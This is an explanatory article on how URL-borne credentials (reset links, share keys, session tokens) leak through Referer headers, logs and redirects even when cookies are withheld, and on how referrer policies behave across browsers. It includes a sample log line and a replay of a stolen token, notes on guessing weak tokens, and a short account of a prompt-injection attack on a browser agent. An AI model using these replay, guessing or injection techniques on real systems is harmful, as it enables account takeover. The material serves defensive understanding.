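# How browsing and testing agents leak credentials through URLs and Referer headers, even without cookies

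## How does a URL come to hold a credential, and how does an agent come to hold the URL?

A browsing agent is a program that uses a language model to open web pages, fill in forms and send requests on someone's behalf. A testing agent does much the same to check a website for faults or security holes, usually while logged in. Both work with URLs (web addresses), and some URLs contain a secret, such as a password-reset code, the key to a private file, or a string that identifies a logged-in user. Anyone who obtains such a URL can usually use it. The URL can reach another company's server during ordinary page loading, with no attacker involved, and deleting cookies does not prevent that.

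### A request and an address, taken apart

To open a page, a browser sends a request to a server using the HTTP protocol, and the server sends back a response. Mozilla's *Overview of HTTP* lists the parts of a request. The first is a method, such as GET to fetch something or POST to submit something, followed by the path of the thing wanted and the protocol version. Optional headers follow, which are named lines of extra information. Some methods also have a body, which holds submitted content such as the fields of a form.

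Here is an invented address for an invoice page:

`https://app.example:8443/invoices/view?id=88&session=k3Vq9TzL#totals`

The scheme is `https`, the host is `app.example` and the port is `8443` (most addresses leave the port out and the browser uses the standard one). The path is `/invoices/view`. Everything from the question mark to the # sign is the query, a list of names and values for the server to use. The part after the # is the fragment, which usually marks a place on the page. A browser that opens this address sends something close to this:

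```
GET /invoices/view?id=88&session=k3Vq9TzL HTTP/1.1
Host: app.example:8443
Accept-Language: en
Cookie: theme=dark
```

The session value travels in the first line of the request, so the server receives it whether or not the browser attaches a cookie. Mozilla's *What is a URL?* explains that browsers never send the fragment with the request, though scripts running on the page can read it. HTTPS encrypts the whole message in transit, so the risk lies mostly in how the browser and server handle and log the URL afterwards. An older form of URL puts a username and password before the host, as in `https://name:password@app.example/`. Mozilla describes this form as deprecated, but it is tempting to leave in a test script.

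A page's origin is its scheme, host and port. By default, browsers prevent a page from one origin from reading the contents of a page from another, but they let pages load files from other origins, and most pages do. After fetching the main document, the browser sends a separate request for each image, script and frame it refers to (its subresources). Many of these requests go to third parties, meaning servers run by someone other than the site the agent is working on, such as an analytics firm or a font host. Each request may carry a Referer header (the standard's misspelling of "referrer") containing some or all of the address of the page that caused it.

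### Why a token is as good as a password

HTTP does not link one request to the next, so an online shop has to keep track of a customer's basket or login itself. After login, the server issues a session token, a string that identifies the user's session, and the browser sends it back with each later request. The token is usually sent in a cookie, a value that the browser stores for a site and returns in the Cookie header.

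NIST's *Session Management* explains that a session continues because the user's software possesses a secret, which it can either present directly or prove cryptographically that it has. Ordinary cookies and most tokens in URLs are presented directly. Jones and Hardt (2012), in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, call such a token a bearer token, meaning that any party that has it can use it in any way that any other party that has it can.

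The server therefore treats a thief who presents the token as the user. In one way, the token is more useful to the thief than the password, because the login has already happened and the server does not ask again for the code on the user's phone. However, some tokens give access to only a single file.

A token grants the same access wherever it sits in the request. Jones and Hardt show one request with the same token in the Authorization header, in a form body and in the URL query. They advise against using the query, mainly because servers are likely to log the URL, and include it only because people were already doing it. *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security*, guidance published in January 2025 by the IETF, the internet's main protocol standards body, goes further and prohibits client software from putting access tokens in a URL query, though it acknowledges that websites often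 do so in practice.

Expiry, single use and binding each affect how useful a stolen token is. An expiry time limits how long a thief can use the token. NIST requires two time limits on a session, one counted from login and one from the last activity. The second does little against a thief who keeps using the session, because activity resets it.

A server accepts a single-use secret only once. OAuth, the protocol behind most "sign in with" buttons, uses this kind of secret. The company that holds the user's account issues a short code, and the app exchanges it for an access token. The code must then stop working. The IETF notes that an attacker who redeems the code before the app does still gets in, so it recommends that the server cancel every token issued on a code if anyone presents the code a second time. An agent can give an attacker much longer to use a secret first. If an agent reads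 a single-use reset link in an inbox and copies it into its notes without opening it, the link still works until it expires.

Binding ties a credential to something a thief lacks. For OAuth codes, the usual method is PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange). The app generates a random secret, sends only its hash at the start, and must later present the secret itself to redeem the code, so a stranger who copies the code from a URL can't redeem it. *Protecting Cookies with Device Bound Session Credentials* (Ackerman, Rubery and Ehinger, 2026) describes Google's counterpart for whole sessions. Chrome creates a key pair inside the computer's security chip, from which nobody can export the private half, and the site issues short-lived cookies only while Chrome proves that it has the key. A stolen cookie soon expires, and the thief can't renew it. Google turned this on by default for Workspace users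 of Chrome on Windows in May 2026, according to its *Prevent account takeovers with Device Bound Session Credentials (DBSC)* (2026).

That helps against malware that steals cookies, but it doesn't protect a reset code or a file link in a URL, because neither is tied to such a key.

### Why designers put secrets in addresses

There is usually a reason for putting a secret in a URL, despite the risks. Tennison's *Good Practices for Capability URLs*, written for the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which sets web standards, collects these reasons and names the pattern. A capability URL is an address that itself grants access to whoever has it.

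The clearest example is the password reset link. The user cannot log in, so the link has to work without a login. Emailing the old password would be worse, since the site would have to send it, and perhaps store it, as readable text. A reset link can expire after one visit and lead to a page that makes the user choose a new password. Emailed sign-in links extend the idea by replacing the password altogether.

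Sites also put credentials in URLs to make sharing easier. Tennison's examples include the private address of a Google calendar, secret code snippets on GitHub and the administration link of a Doodle poll. The recipient needs no account and can pass the link on to someone the sender has never met. This is convenient for arranging a meeting, but it also means that anyone who gets the link can use it. If one recipient leaks the link, the owner generally has to revoke it for everybody.

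Some sites put a secret in the URL because they cannot safely send their login cookie. For example, a service that hosts files from untrusted users may serve each user's files from a separate domain to keep a malicious file from acting with the main site's privileges. Sending the main site's login cookie to that domain would defeat the separation, so the service puts a secret in the file's URL instead.

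OAuth codes end up in URLs because the sign-in provider sends them to the app by redirecting the browser, and the redirect carries its data in the address. The IETF gives the example `client.example/redirection_endpoint?code=abcd`. The provider can instead send the code in a form body, which the IETF lists as a countermeasure.

Cloud storage services offer signed file links, which carry authentication data in the URL's query. *Authenticating Requests*, from Amazon's cloud division, AWS, explains that this lets a developer express a request entirely in a URL, which a program, a browser or a customer without an account can then use. AWS's *Download and upload objects with presigned URLs* calls these links bearer tokens. They work repeatedly until they expire, which can be up to 12 hours for a link made in the web console and up to seven days for one made with Amazon's command-line tool or programming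 libraries. A link stops working sooner if the credential used to sign it becomes invalid. Some links allow uploads, which replace any file already stored under the same name. The owner can restrict use to particular networks, which is a form of binding.

Developers also put credentials in the URLs of preview copies of unreleased sites. The public must not find these copies, but clients and automated tests need to get in without an account, so the URL contains a random string or a parameter that skips the login page.

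Designers have little choice with WebSockets, which are connections that stay open so that both sides can send messages at any time, as in a chat window. The browser interface that opens a WebSocket doesn't let the page's code set an Authorization header. If the page and the agent's server share an origin, the browser sends its cookies, and the server can use those instead. *Cross-domain authentication*, part of the infrastructure company Cloudflare's documentation for developers who build agents on its platform, covers the case where the origins differ and the developer can't rely on a cookie. It recommends putting a short-lived token in the query of the connection address and checking it on the server. Cloudflare warns that tokens in URLs may end up in logs and recommends lifetimes of minutes, not hours. Test scripts that run outside the browser can generally set the header, so their developers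 have less reason to put a token in the query.

People still use capability URLs despite an early objection. When the W3C published a first draft of Tennison's advice in February 2014, one reader replied on its mailing list, in *Comments on "Good Practices for Capability URLs" FPWD*, that the web is not generally designed to keep URLs secret and that encouraging such addresses was a mistake. The finished document supports this objection. It notes that the URLs appear on screen, in browser history and in server logs, that browsers may send them to a central service that checks for phishing, and that link shorteners and history-syncing services collect them. Tennison recommends weighing the risk case by case and limiting the damage with expiry and random values of 120 bits or more.

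### What a leaked link opened

*The Tragedy of Convenience* (Danish, Acharya and colleagues, 2026) examines links that companies send by text message. The researchers collected 33,128,103 messages from 25 public SMS gateways, websites that lend out disposable phone numbers and show every message received on them. The messages contained 322,949 distinct URLs. In July 2025, at least a year after the messages arrived, the researchers opened each URL in an automated browser and saved a screenshot, the network traffic and the page's HTML. A language model running on their own machines flagged pages that seemed to show personal data, and two reviewers checked every flagged page.

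They confirmed 701 URLs, at 177 services, that exposed a user's personal data. At 172 of those services, the cause was a tokenised link, where the server checked only the string in the address. At the other five, the personal data was in the URL itself or in a redirect. All 701 URLs still worked, and almost 46% were at least two years old.

The researchers had already found these services leaking, so 172 out of 177 is not an estimate of how many companies design their links this way. The delay also removed most short-lived links before the count, as the researchers intended. The study does show that real companies, 19 of them in finance, use long-lived bearer links, and that having the link was enough to get access.

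One link opened a pre-filled loan application with the person's name, date of birth, marital status, address, bank account number and state identity card number. Another loan application exposed a social security number in the network traffic. A link from iHire, a job site, opened a page that greeted the user by first name. Clicking "Continue" led to the logged-in profile, where a visitor could change the email address and password without further checks. Fourteen services let the holder of a link edit personal data, five gave access to the account, and iHire did both. Server responses from 76 services also held more personal data than the page displayed, so an agent that reads responses directly can see data that the page doesn't show.

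A leaked link can also endanger people who never received it, if it helps an attacker guess other people's links. Entropy measures, in bits, how hard a token is to guess. A token of *L* characters, each drawn at random from an alphabet of *A* symbols, has *L* × log₂ *A* bits, and each extra bit doubles the number of possibilities. NIST's minimum for session secrets is 64 bits, or about 18 billion billion values. Of the 172 services with tokenised links, 125 (72.67%) fell below that minimum.

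iHire's tokens had five letters or digits. If capitals count separately, that allows about 916 million values, or just under 30 bits; if they do not, about 60 million. The company reports 3.45 million members active in a month. With one live link for each of them, a random guess would succeed about once in 265 tries in the first case and once in 18 in the second. The researchers reached another person's account after two changes to the token. They may have been lucky, but more likely there were far more live links than members.

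Whether an attacker could harvest a whole service depends on how many of the possible tokens are in use, as well as on their entropy. Danish and colleagues chose not to measure this for ethical reasons. They made at most ten manual changes per token and reached someone else's data at 13 of the 125. The entropy formula can also overstate how secure a service's tokens are. One car-transport firm used a sequential order number plus two letters, so adding one to the number brought up the next customer's quote.

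### Three ways an agent browses

HTTP does not require a browser. Requests come from a user agent, which Mozilla defines as any tool that acts for the user. Language-model agents use roughly three kinds of tool.

The first is a full browser, which the agent controls through an automation library such as Playwright, which Danish and colleagues used. The browser keeps cookies, follows redirects, loads third-party files and runs their scripts, as it would for a person. Secrets appear in its address bar, such as an OAuth code just after sign-in, and many agent set-ups pass the current address to the model at every step along with the page's text or a screenshot. Testing agents also tend to save the same records as the SMS researchers, including network logs, which contain the full address of every request they record. The researchers deleted their logs when the study ended, but a team that attaches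 such logs to bug reports usually keeps them.

An agent can also use a plain HTTP client, such as curl or a few lines of Python. The client sends one request and gets one response, without loading images or running scripts, and by default it sends no Referer header when given a URL directly. The agent typically gets these URLs from configuration, such as a preview address with its bypass parameter, a signed link to a test file, or an address with a username and password in front. It reads the configuration files at the start of a job, so the URLs enter the model's context as plain text before the agent opens any of them.

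The remaining way is a fetch tool run by the model's provider. The model writes a URL, and the provider's server requests the page and returns its text. The page's owner sees a request from the provider's server, and the provider receives the full URL. The tool generally lacks the user's cookies, so it cannot open a page that requires a login. A user who wants help with a private document often pastes in a share link instead.

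An agent with access to email can come across secrets whichever of these tools it uses. To test a sign-up form, it has to find the confirmation message and open the link inside, and the same inbox may hold password reset links, sign-in links and invitations to shared files. A fetch tool without cookies can open those links as easily as the user's own browser can, because the server checks only what is in the URL.

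## Why does withholding cookies not stop the leak?

Withholding an agent's cookies does not stop it from leaking a token in a URL. Browsers and HTTP clients offer several ways to withhold cookies, but each one controls only a single request header or data store, and the token depends on neither.

### What each cookie control does

*Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2025), the draft revision of the internet's cookie standard, defines the Set-Cookie header, which a server uses to give the browser a cookie, and the Cookie header, which the browser uses to return it. Every cookie control interrupts that exchange at some point.

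An agent that starts with an empty browser profile has no stored cookies or other saved data, such as the contents of localStorage, which a site's scripts can read and write. But a testing agent usually logs in soon afterwards, and the profile then holds a session cookie.

Blocking third-party cookies affects which requests carry a cookie. As W3C explains in its work on cross-site cookie blocking, browsers traditionally attach a cookie to every request within its scope, generally a domain and a path, even when a page on another site caused the request. Blocking ends that for cross-site requests. A site can ask for a similar restriction on its own cookie with the SameSite attribute. The value `Lax` keeps the cookie out of cross-site requests for images and other subresources.

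Both measures stop another site's page from using the visitor's login at app.example. A leaked address goes the opposite way, from a page at app.example to the other site.

The HttpOnly attribute stops scripts from reading a cookie, but the browser still sends it. A client can also drop the Cookie header. Code running in a browser can do much the same with a request's `credentials` setting. Mozilla's developer documentation (MDN, *Request*) lists three values for it: `omit` never sends or receives cookies, `same-origin` (the default) sends them only to the calling script's own origin, and `include` always sends them.

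The name of the `credentials` setting can mislead developers, because a request with `credentials: "omit"` still sends any session token in its URL. The WHATWG standard that browsers follow when they make requests defines credentials as cookies, TLS client certificates (files that identify a computer when it opens an encrypted connection) and authentication entries (usernames and passwords that the browser has saved for a site's built-in HTTP login).

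### The same request with and without cookies

Suppose an agent is reading a report at `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN`. The page includes a small image from stats.example, an analytics company, and its referrer policy lets the full address go to other sites (`unsafe-url` is one value that does). To fetch the image, the browser sends something like this:

```
GET /pixel.gif HTTP/1.1
Host: stats.example
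Referer: https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN
Sec-Fetch-Dest: image
Sec-Fetch-Mode: no-cors
Sec-Fetch-Site: cross-site
Cookie: visitor=7f21c0
```

W3C's *Fetch Metadata Request Headers* (2021) gives the three Sec-Fetch lines as an example of what a browser adds when a page loads an image from another site. They help the receiving server decide whether to reject the request and contain no secrets. The cookie belongs to stats.example, which set it on an earlier visit. No setting would make the browser send app.example's cookie to stats.example.

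Now the operator turns cookies off and runs the agent again:

```
GET /pixel.gif HTTP/1.1
Host: stats.example
Referer: https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN
Sec-Fetch-Dest: image
Sec-Fetch-Mode: no-cors
Sec-Fetch-Site: cross-site
```

Stats.example can no longer use its cookie to recognise a returning visitor, which is a real gain in privacy. It still receives the token. Web servers commonly write the Referer into their access logs, so the company may now hold a line like this without anyone there having meant to collect it:

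```
198.51.100.7 "GET /pixel.gif HTTP/1.1" 200 "https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN"
```

Anyone who can read the log can copy the address and open it on another computer:

```
GET /report?session=TOKEN HTTP/1.1
Host: app.example
```

This request has no cookie and no connection to the agent's browser. The server at app.example looks up TOKEN, finds the user's session and returns the report. If the session allows changes, the stranger can make those too. Anyone with access to the old logs at stats.example, including a contractor or an intruder, can copy the same line.

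In *Remediating Session Token in URL Issues*, a help page from the security-ratings company Bitsight, Conry says that URLs containing session tokens also end up in proxy servers, bookmarks and forwarded emails. Bitsight scans URLs for known session-token patterns but does not count them in a company's rating, so a company with a good rating may still have the problem.

In March 2025 the bug-bounty platform huntr published a vulnerability record, with a severity of 7.6 out of 10, for Open WebUI, a chat interface that organisations run themselves to use language models. According to the record, an attacker could put an image in a chat, and when an administrator viewed it, the image request would carry the administrator's session cookie to the attacker's server. Open WebUI's *CVE-2024-7053* (2026) gives four reasons why this can't happen: the browser sends cookies only to their own domain, HttpOnly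 hides this cookie from scripts, `SameSite=Lax` keeps it out of cross-site image requests, and displaying an image doesn't run scripts. Huntr agreed to withdraw the record in August 2026.

Open WebUI was right about the cookie, but its four reasons don't cover a token in the URL of the page showing the image. Under a referrer policy like the one at app.example, the image request would send that token to the attacker in the Referer header.

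### Which carriers the controls reach

The table shows how each cookie control affects a secret in each place it can travel. "None" means the control does not remove the secret from that place.

| Carrier | Empty profile | Third-party blocking and SameSite | HttpOnly | Dropping the Cookie header |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cookie header | Nothing to send until the agent logs in | Removes it from cross-site requests | None | Removes it |
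| Requested URL | None | None | None | None |
| Referer header | None | None | None | None |
| Authorization and custom headers | Removes logins saved in the browser | None | None | None |
| Request body | None | None | None | None |
| Scripts reading the address | None | None | Hides the cookie, not the address | None |

The row for Authorization and custom headers needs qualification. Setting `credentials: "omit"` drops the Cookie header and any Authorization header that the browser would have built from a saved login, but it doesn't affect headers that the application's own code adds. http.dev's *Access-Control-Allow-Credentials* says such a header "travels either way".

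Before a script can send an Authorization header to another origin, the browser sends a preflight request to check whether the receiving server accepts it. Under WHATWG's standard, the server must name Authorization explicitly in its response, and a wildcard is not enough. The check doesn't stop a recipient who wants the token, because their server can accept the header. A plain HTTP client such as curl sends no preflight.

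The preflight can leak the page's address. It carries no cookies, but under the standard it takes its referrer and referrer policy from the request it precedes. If the policy allows the full address, the receiving server can log it even if the server then refuses the main request.

Open WebUI also shows why it matters where a site keeps its token. Infosecurity Magazine's *High-Severity Flaw in Open WebUI Affects AI Connections* describes a later flaw, which Cato Networks researchers found and the developers have since patched. Open WebUI has an optional feature for connecting to an outside model server. A malicious server could send a message that made the user's browser run the attacker's JavaScript. The script could then read the login token from localStorage, and the token gave full access to the account, including chats, uploaded files and API keys. HttpOnly works only on cookies, so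 it could not protect the token.

### How a session can end up in a URL anyway

Even a login that starts in a cookie can end up in an address. SiteMinder, a Broadcom product that lets people log in once for several websites, does this by default. A browser won't return one domain's cookie to an unrelated domain, so SiteMinder needs another way to carry the login across. Its software on the web server redirects the browser to a "cookie provider" and puts the value of the session cookie, SMSESSION, in the redirect's query string:

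`/siteminderagent/SmMakeCookie.ccc?SMSESSION=-SM-gtRe1W...&PERSIST=0&TARGET=...`

In *smsession cookie is passed and exposed in URL when calling cookie providers*, Broadcom responds to a report that this is a vulnerability by saying that the product works this way by design. Neither HttpOnly nor SameSite affects the redirect, because the server has already copied the cookie's value into the URL. The browser probably moves on from that URL without displaying a page, so the value is more likely to appear in server logs, proxy logs and an agent's saved network trace than in a Referer header.

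Administrators can change the default with a setting called `StoreSessioninServer`, which makes SiteMinder keep the session temporarily on the server and put only an identifier for it in the redirect. This needs a session store on SiteMinder's central server, and administrators have to turn the setting on for every component that takes part in the shared login. Another setting, `SecureURLs`, encrypts the query.

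Withholding cookies can even put a token in a URL that would otherwise not have one. Some web frameworks, including Java's servlet containers, can add the session identifier to a site's own links when a browser returns no cookie. If an operator turns cookies off on such a site, the login may still work, but with `jsessionid` now in the URLs.

A token can also go straight from a tool's own storage into a URL. Coder is a product for setting up remote development environments, and its command `coder open app` opens linked applications. A link could contain the placeholder `$SESSION_TOKEN`, which the tool replaced with the user's real session token. OSV's *CVE-2026-55431* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, reports that the tool did this without checking which host the link led to, and rates the flaw's severity at 7.7 out of 10.

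According to MITRE's *CVE-2026-55431* (2026), only someone who wrote a malicious template for the development environment could control the link, and the victim had to run the command in an environment that used that template. Coder's fix inserts the token only for trusted destinations. Blocking cookies in the browser would not have stopped the leak, because the token was already in the address when the browser opened it.

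### What removing cookies does stop

Removing a cookie does stop an attack that depends on that cookie. A recent example is a flaw that researchers at Sand Security found in Writer, a platform on which companies build AI agents. A July 2026 story on The Hacker News' *session hijacking* page quotes Sand's claim that an outsider could take over a customer's organisation "with nothing more than a link". Writer had fixed the flaw by then.

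In *Industry Updates*, the newsletter writer openmatter describes an attack on Writer users. The attacker built an agent in their own Writer account and sent the victim a link to its live preview. If the victim was signed in to Writer and clicked the link, the preview feature forwarded the victim's session cookie into the preview. The attacker could then reach the victim's private chats, documents and stored model credentials, even though the two belonged to different customers.

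Writer stopped forwarding the cookie, which removed the credential the attack relied on. It also moved previews to a separate origin, which keeps a hostile preview away from Writer's own pages and stored data, even if the preview runs the attacker's code.

An empty profile also limits what an attacker can do through prompt injection, which is text in a page or message that the agent treats as an instruction. Zenity Labs' *Account Takeover via Claude in Chrome* describes an attack on the Anthropic extension that lets Claude act in a user's browser. The injected text got the extension to run code in the browser, and because the victim was logged in to Gmail, the code could read incoming email. It could not have done so in a fresh profile with no Gmail session.

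According to Cyber Security News (2026), Claude.ai's emailed sign-in link had a one-time secret in its fragment. An attacker who read the email could submit that secret to Claude.ai's login system and receive a new session cookie for the victim's account, without the victim's existing cookies. Anyone who gets a valid sign-in link another way could do the same, so an agent with no cookies can still give away a login.

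### When a leaked token is useless

A single-use code may already be useless by the time it leaks, depending on when the server cancels it. If a site cancels a password reset code as soon as the link is opened, the Referer headers that the reset page then sends contain a code that no longer works. If the site cancels the code only when the user submits a new password, the code still works while the page loads its images and scripts. In that case, an agent that opens a reset link only to check that the page displays properly leaves the code working until it expires.

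Expiry also limits the damage. OffSeq's *GHSA-v54h-cp2w-9x4g*, a security advisory on the Coder flaw, says that the attacker could impersonate the user while the token remained valid. A token that lasts five minutes is little use to someone who reads a log the next day, though a program watching requests as they arrive can use it at once. Long-lived links, such as those Danish and colleagues found, lack this protection.

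A value may also be useless on its own. Many sites put an anti-forgery token in forms, and sometimes in URLs, to check that a request came from their own pages. The server accepts the token only with the user's session cookie, which the third party never received. Testers who find a random string in a URL therefore need to check what access it gives before calling it a leaked credential.

Binding a credential to the client that requested it also works. PKCE does this for OAuth codes, so a copied code is useless to a stranger. Chrome's device-bound sessions don't protect a sign-in link, though. The Hacker News quotes Andy Wen of Google as saying that the feature ties the cookie to the device the user authenticated from. A thief who opens a live sign-in link authenticates from their own device, so Chrome would tie the new session to the thief's device.

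## When does a browser send the full page address to another site?

By default, current browsers put only a page's origin, such as `https://app.example/`, in the Referer header of a request to another site. They send the full address, including any token in the query, when the page or one of its elements sets a looser referrer policy. Chromium, the open-source browser that Chrome is built on and most agents use, applies any policy a site sets, but Firefox and Safari override the most permissive ones.

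### How the browser builds the header

W3C's *Referrer Policy* specifies when a browser sends the full page address to another site. A motivating example in its introduction is an application that keeps a session identifier in its URLs and links to other sites. According to the introduction, capability URLs can also leak in ways that a referrer policy does not control.

For each request, the browser usually starts with the address of the document that caused it and removes the username, password and fragment. If more than 4,096 characters remain, it keeps only the origin. Depending on the referrer policy, it then sends no Referer header, only the origin, or everything that remains. From here on, "full address" means the scheme, host, port, path and query.

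A Referer header therefore cannot leak a secret in a fragment, like the one in Claude.ai's emailed sign-in links, or a username and password placed before the host. But reset codes, share keys and file signatures usually sit in the path or query, which the browser keeps. The 4,096-character limit rarely helps, because most addresses containing tokens are much shorter.

Cutting the address down to its origin does not protect a secret in the host name. If a developer hides an unreleased site at `https://k3vq9tzl.preview.example/`, the origin contains the whole secret, and the default policy sends it to every third party whose files the preview loads.

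### The eight values

The table shows what the browser sends under each policy.

| Policy | To the same origin | To another origin over HTTPS | From an HTTPS page to plain HTTP |
|---|---|---|---|
| `no-referrer` | Nothing | Nothing | Nothing |
| `same-origin` | Full address | Nothing | Nothing |
| `strict-origin` | Origin | Origin | Nothing |
| `strict-origin-when-cross-origin` (default) | Full address | Origin | Nothing |
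| `origin` | Origin | Origin | Origin |
| `origin-when-cross-origin` | Full address | Origin | Origin |
| `no-referrer-when-downgrade` | Full address | Full address | Nothing |
| `unsafe-url` | Full address | Full address | Full address |

Suppose a testing agent has opened `https://tester:pw1@app.example/report?session=TOKEN#totals`. The page loads a stylesheet from its own server and an image from stats.example. The agent then clicks a link to old.example, which still uses plain HTTP. Under four of the policies, the Referer header contains the following:

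| Policy | Stylesheet on app.example | Image on stats.example | Link to old.example |
|---|---|---|---|
| `strict-origin` | `https://app.example/` | `https://app.example/` | No header |
| `strict-origin-when-cross-origin` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` | `https://app.example/` | No header |
| `no-referrer-when-downgrade` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` | No header |
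| `unsafe-url` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` | `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` |

Under `no-referrer-when-downgrade`, the browser withholds the address only when a request goes from HTTPS to unencrypted HTTP. Such requests are now rare. In *Referrer Policy*, a 2025 study that shares its title with the specification, Zagi, Moti and Acar captured about 12 million requests and found that only 2.15% used plain HTTP. In practice, the browser therefore sends the full address to nearly every third party under this policy. With `unsafe-url`, it also sends the full address over plain HTTP, where anyone on the network path can read it.

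The strictest value, `no-referrer`, may cause a testing agent's form submissions to fail. Browsers send a separate Origin header with form submissions, and this header contains no path or query. According to MDN's *Referrer-Policy header*, `no-referrer` makes the browser send `null` there instead of the real origin. A server that checks the header before accepting a form may then reject the agent's submission, and the agent may report a fault that ordinary users never see.

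### Which setting takes effect

A site can set a referrer policy for a whole document with a `Referrer-Policy` response header or a `<meta name="referrer">` tag in the HTML. It can also set a policy for a single link, image, frame or script with a `referrerpolicy` attribute. If a link is marked `rel="noreferrer"`, the browser sends no Referer when someone follows it.

An element's referrer policy overrides the document's, and a valid meta tag overrides the response header. Either override can be looser than the policy it replaces. WHATWG's *The elements of HTML* specifies that the browser changes the document's policy whenever a script or the page's own markup inserts or edits such a meta tag. The latest change applies, and deleting the tag does not restore the earlier policy.

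Suppose app.example's server sends `Referrer-Policy: no-referrer`, but a page template contains `<meta name="referrer" content="always">`. Browsers still accept `always` as an old name for `unsafe-url`, so they send the page's full address with requests to any site. A tester who checked only the response header would conclude that the page was safe. Zagi and colleagues relied on Chrome's debugging protocol instead because it reports the policy that the browser worked out for each request.

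In a 2016 discussion on W3C's mailing list, Emily Stark of Google explained that a valid referrer policy in a meta tag overrides the one in the header. Toomey, an engineer at GitHub, then raised the possibility of ranking the policies by strictness so that a later setting could only tighten an earlier one. The specification still lets the meta tag override the header.

The same rule applies within a single header, where a server can list several values separated by commas and the browser uses the last one it recognises. MDN gives the example `no-referrer, strict-origin-when-cross-origin`, in which the first value is only a fallback for browsers that don't know the second. With this header, a modern browser sends the origin to other sites and the full address to the site itself, although a developer who assumes the strictest value wins would expect it to send no Referer.

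Browsers ignore a misspelled referrer policy and use whatever policy would otherwise apply. Zagi and colleagues found meta tags that contained `noreferrer`. That is the correct spelling for the link attribute, but the meta tag requires `no-referrer`.

The browser uses the referrer policy in force when it creates a request. If a page requests an image before a script inserts a strict meta tag, the browser sends that request under the earlier policy.

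#### Frames and stylesheets

A frame is a page embedded in another page. Under the HTML standard (WHATWG's *Loading web pages*), a frame that loads an ordinary web address takes its referrer policy from its own server's response, or uses the default if that response sets none. Only documents without a server response of their own copy a policy from elsewhere. These include `about:blank`, `data:` addresses and frames whose HTML is written in a `srcdoc` attribute in the parent page. Zagi and colleagues describe frames as inheriting the policy of the page that contains them, which is broader than the standard's rule.

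The `srcdoc` case can matter for agents that read messages, because a webmail or chat application may display someone else's HTML in a `srcdoc` frame. When an image in the frame loads, the browser uses the surrounding page's address as the referrer and applies that page's policy. If the policy is permissive, the browser can send the application's address to whoever hosts the image. If the developer sandboxes the frame so that it has its own origin, the browser sends no Referer.

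When a page loads an ordinary frame, the browser sends the parent page's address with the request, subject to the parent's referrer policy or the `referrerpolicy` attribute on the frame element. Requests made from inside the frame carry the frame's address.

When an external stylesheet loads a font or background image, the Referer contains the stylesheet's address, so a token in the page's address does not reach the file's host. For styles written in the page itself, the browser uses the page's address and policy. Since version 26.2, released in December 2025, Safari has let developers set a referrer policy for a single file that a stylesheet loads. Web Platform DX's *referrer-policy() for url()* lists no other browser with this feature.

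### The 2020 change of default

Before 2020, the default referrer policy was `no-referrer-when-downgrade`. If an HTTPS site didn't set its own policy, its pages sent their full addresses to every HTTPS analytics firm, font host and advertising network they used.

Zagi and colleagues describe two leaks of this kind. The train-ticket site trainline.eu leaked unique user tokens in the Referer header, and third parties could have used those tokens to open customers' bookings without logging in. In 2021, someone found that UPchieve, an online tutoring and counselling site whose users probably include many high-school students, leaked password reset tokens to a third party. Anyone who received a token that was still valid could have set a new password and taken over the account. Chrome had already changed its default by then, so a token could have leaked in the Referer header only if the user's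 browser still had the old default or the page set a looser policy than the new one.

The study also cites work by Kaleli and colleagues on online collaboration services, which found that a link in a shared file could expose the file's own secret URL to the outside site. An agent that follows links in a shared document could expose the URL just as a person could.

Under the new default, `strict-origin-when-cross-origin`, the third party in each of these cases would have received only the site's origin. Can I use's browser support table, *headers HTTP header*, lists Chrome 85, Edge 85, Firefox 87 and Safari 15 as the first versions with this default. Web Platform DX's *Referrer policy* dates the Chrome and Edge releases to August 2020, Firefox's to March 2021 and Safari's to September 2021. W3C changed the specification in November 2020, after Chrome had adopted the default.

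Much of the change's value is that it protects users of sites whose developers did nothing. It does not protect an agent running on a browser older than these versions.

### What still gets through

A site that sets a permissive policy overrides the new default. Some sites may do this on purpose, because advertisers and affiliate partners like to know exactly which page sent them a visitor. Others may have set `no-referrer-when-downgrade` when it was the default, and browser updates don't change a site's configuration.

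Advertising can also add the permissive setting to a page. In Zagi and colleagues' crawl from San Francisco, 537 sites had a frame element with `referrerpolicy="unsafe-url"`. On 405 of them, the frame came from rubiconproject.com, which belongs to the advertising company Magnite. If such a frame is directly in a page that an agent has opened, Chromium sends the page's full address to the advertising company, even if the site's own header is strict.

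The default referrer policy still sends the full address with requests to the same origin, because it treats an origin as having a single owner. Some origins are shared, however. Suppose docs.example gives each customer a folder and passes requests for that folder to the customer's own server. If an agent opens `https://docs.example/acme/invite?key=TOKEN` and clicks a link to `https://docs.example/zenith/`, the scheme, host and port match, so the browser sends Acme's invitation key to Zenith's server in the Referer header.

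The same thing happens when a company makes an outside service appear under its own address. For example, it may forward requests under `app.example/metrics/` to an analytics vendor, partly so that ad blockers don't block them. If the forwarding server passes on the Referer header, the vendor receives full page addresses under the default policy.

The `strict-origin` and `no-referrer` policies close this gap, but `same-origin` does not. Giving each customer a subdomain closes it even under the default policy, because two subdomains are different origins. Separate subdomains also stop one customer's scripts from reading another's pages, which no referrer policy can do.

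### Chromium, Firefox, Safari and Brave

In the earlier report page example, stats.example received the token because the page had set `unsafe-url` and the browser applied it. Chrome, Edge and Opera apply all eight Referrer-Policy values. Firefox and Safari would have sent stats.example only `https://app.example/`.

Mozilla announced in an *intent-to-prototype* that Firefox would ignore `unsafe-url`, `no-referrer-when-downgrade` and `origin-when-cross-origin` for requests to other sites. It first tried this in Firefox 92, behind a preference. When someone later reported that Firefox was ignoring `unsafe-url` on a frame from another site, Mozilla replied that this was expected. According to a comment on the same report, Chrome's developers had considered the change and given up on it.

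Firefox and Safari apply this protection only between sites. A site includes all the subdomains of a registered domain, so `reports.app.example` and `help.app.example` are different origins on the same site. Rautenstrauch (2024), in *Referrer-Policy 'unsafe-url' and co. supported for same-site URLs*, reported that in WebKit, Safari's engine, a subdomain with `unsafe-url` still sent its full address to another host on the same site. Sam Sneddon replied that Safari's tracking protection trims the header after the browser has applied the policy, and only for requests to other sites. Rautenstrauch added that Firefox seemed to do the same.

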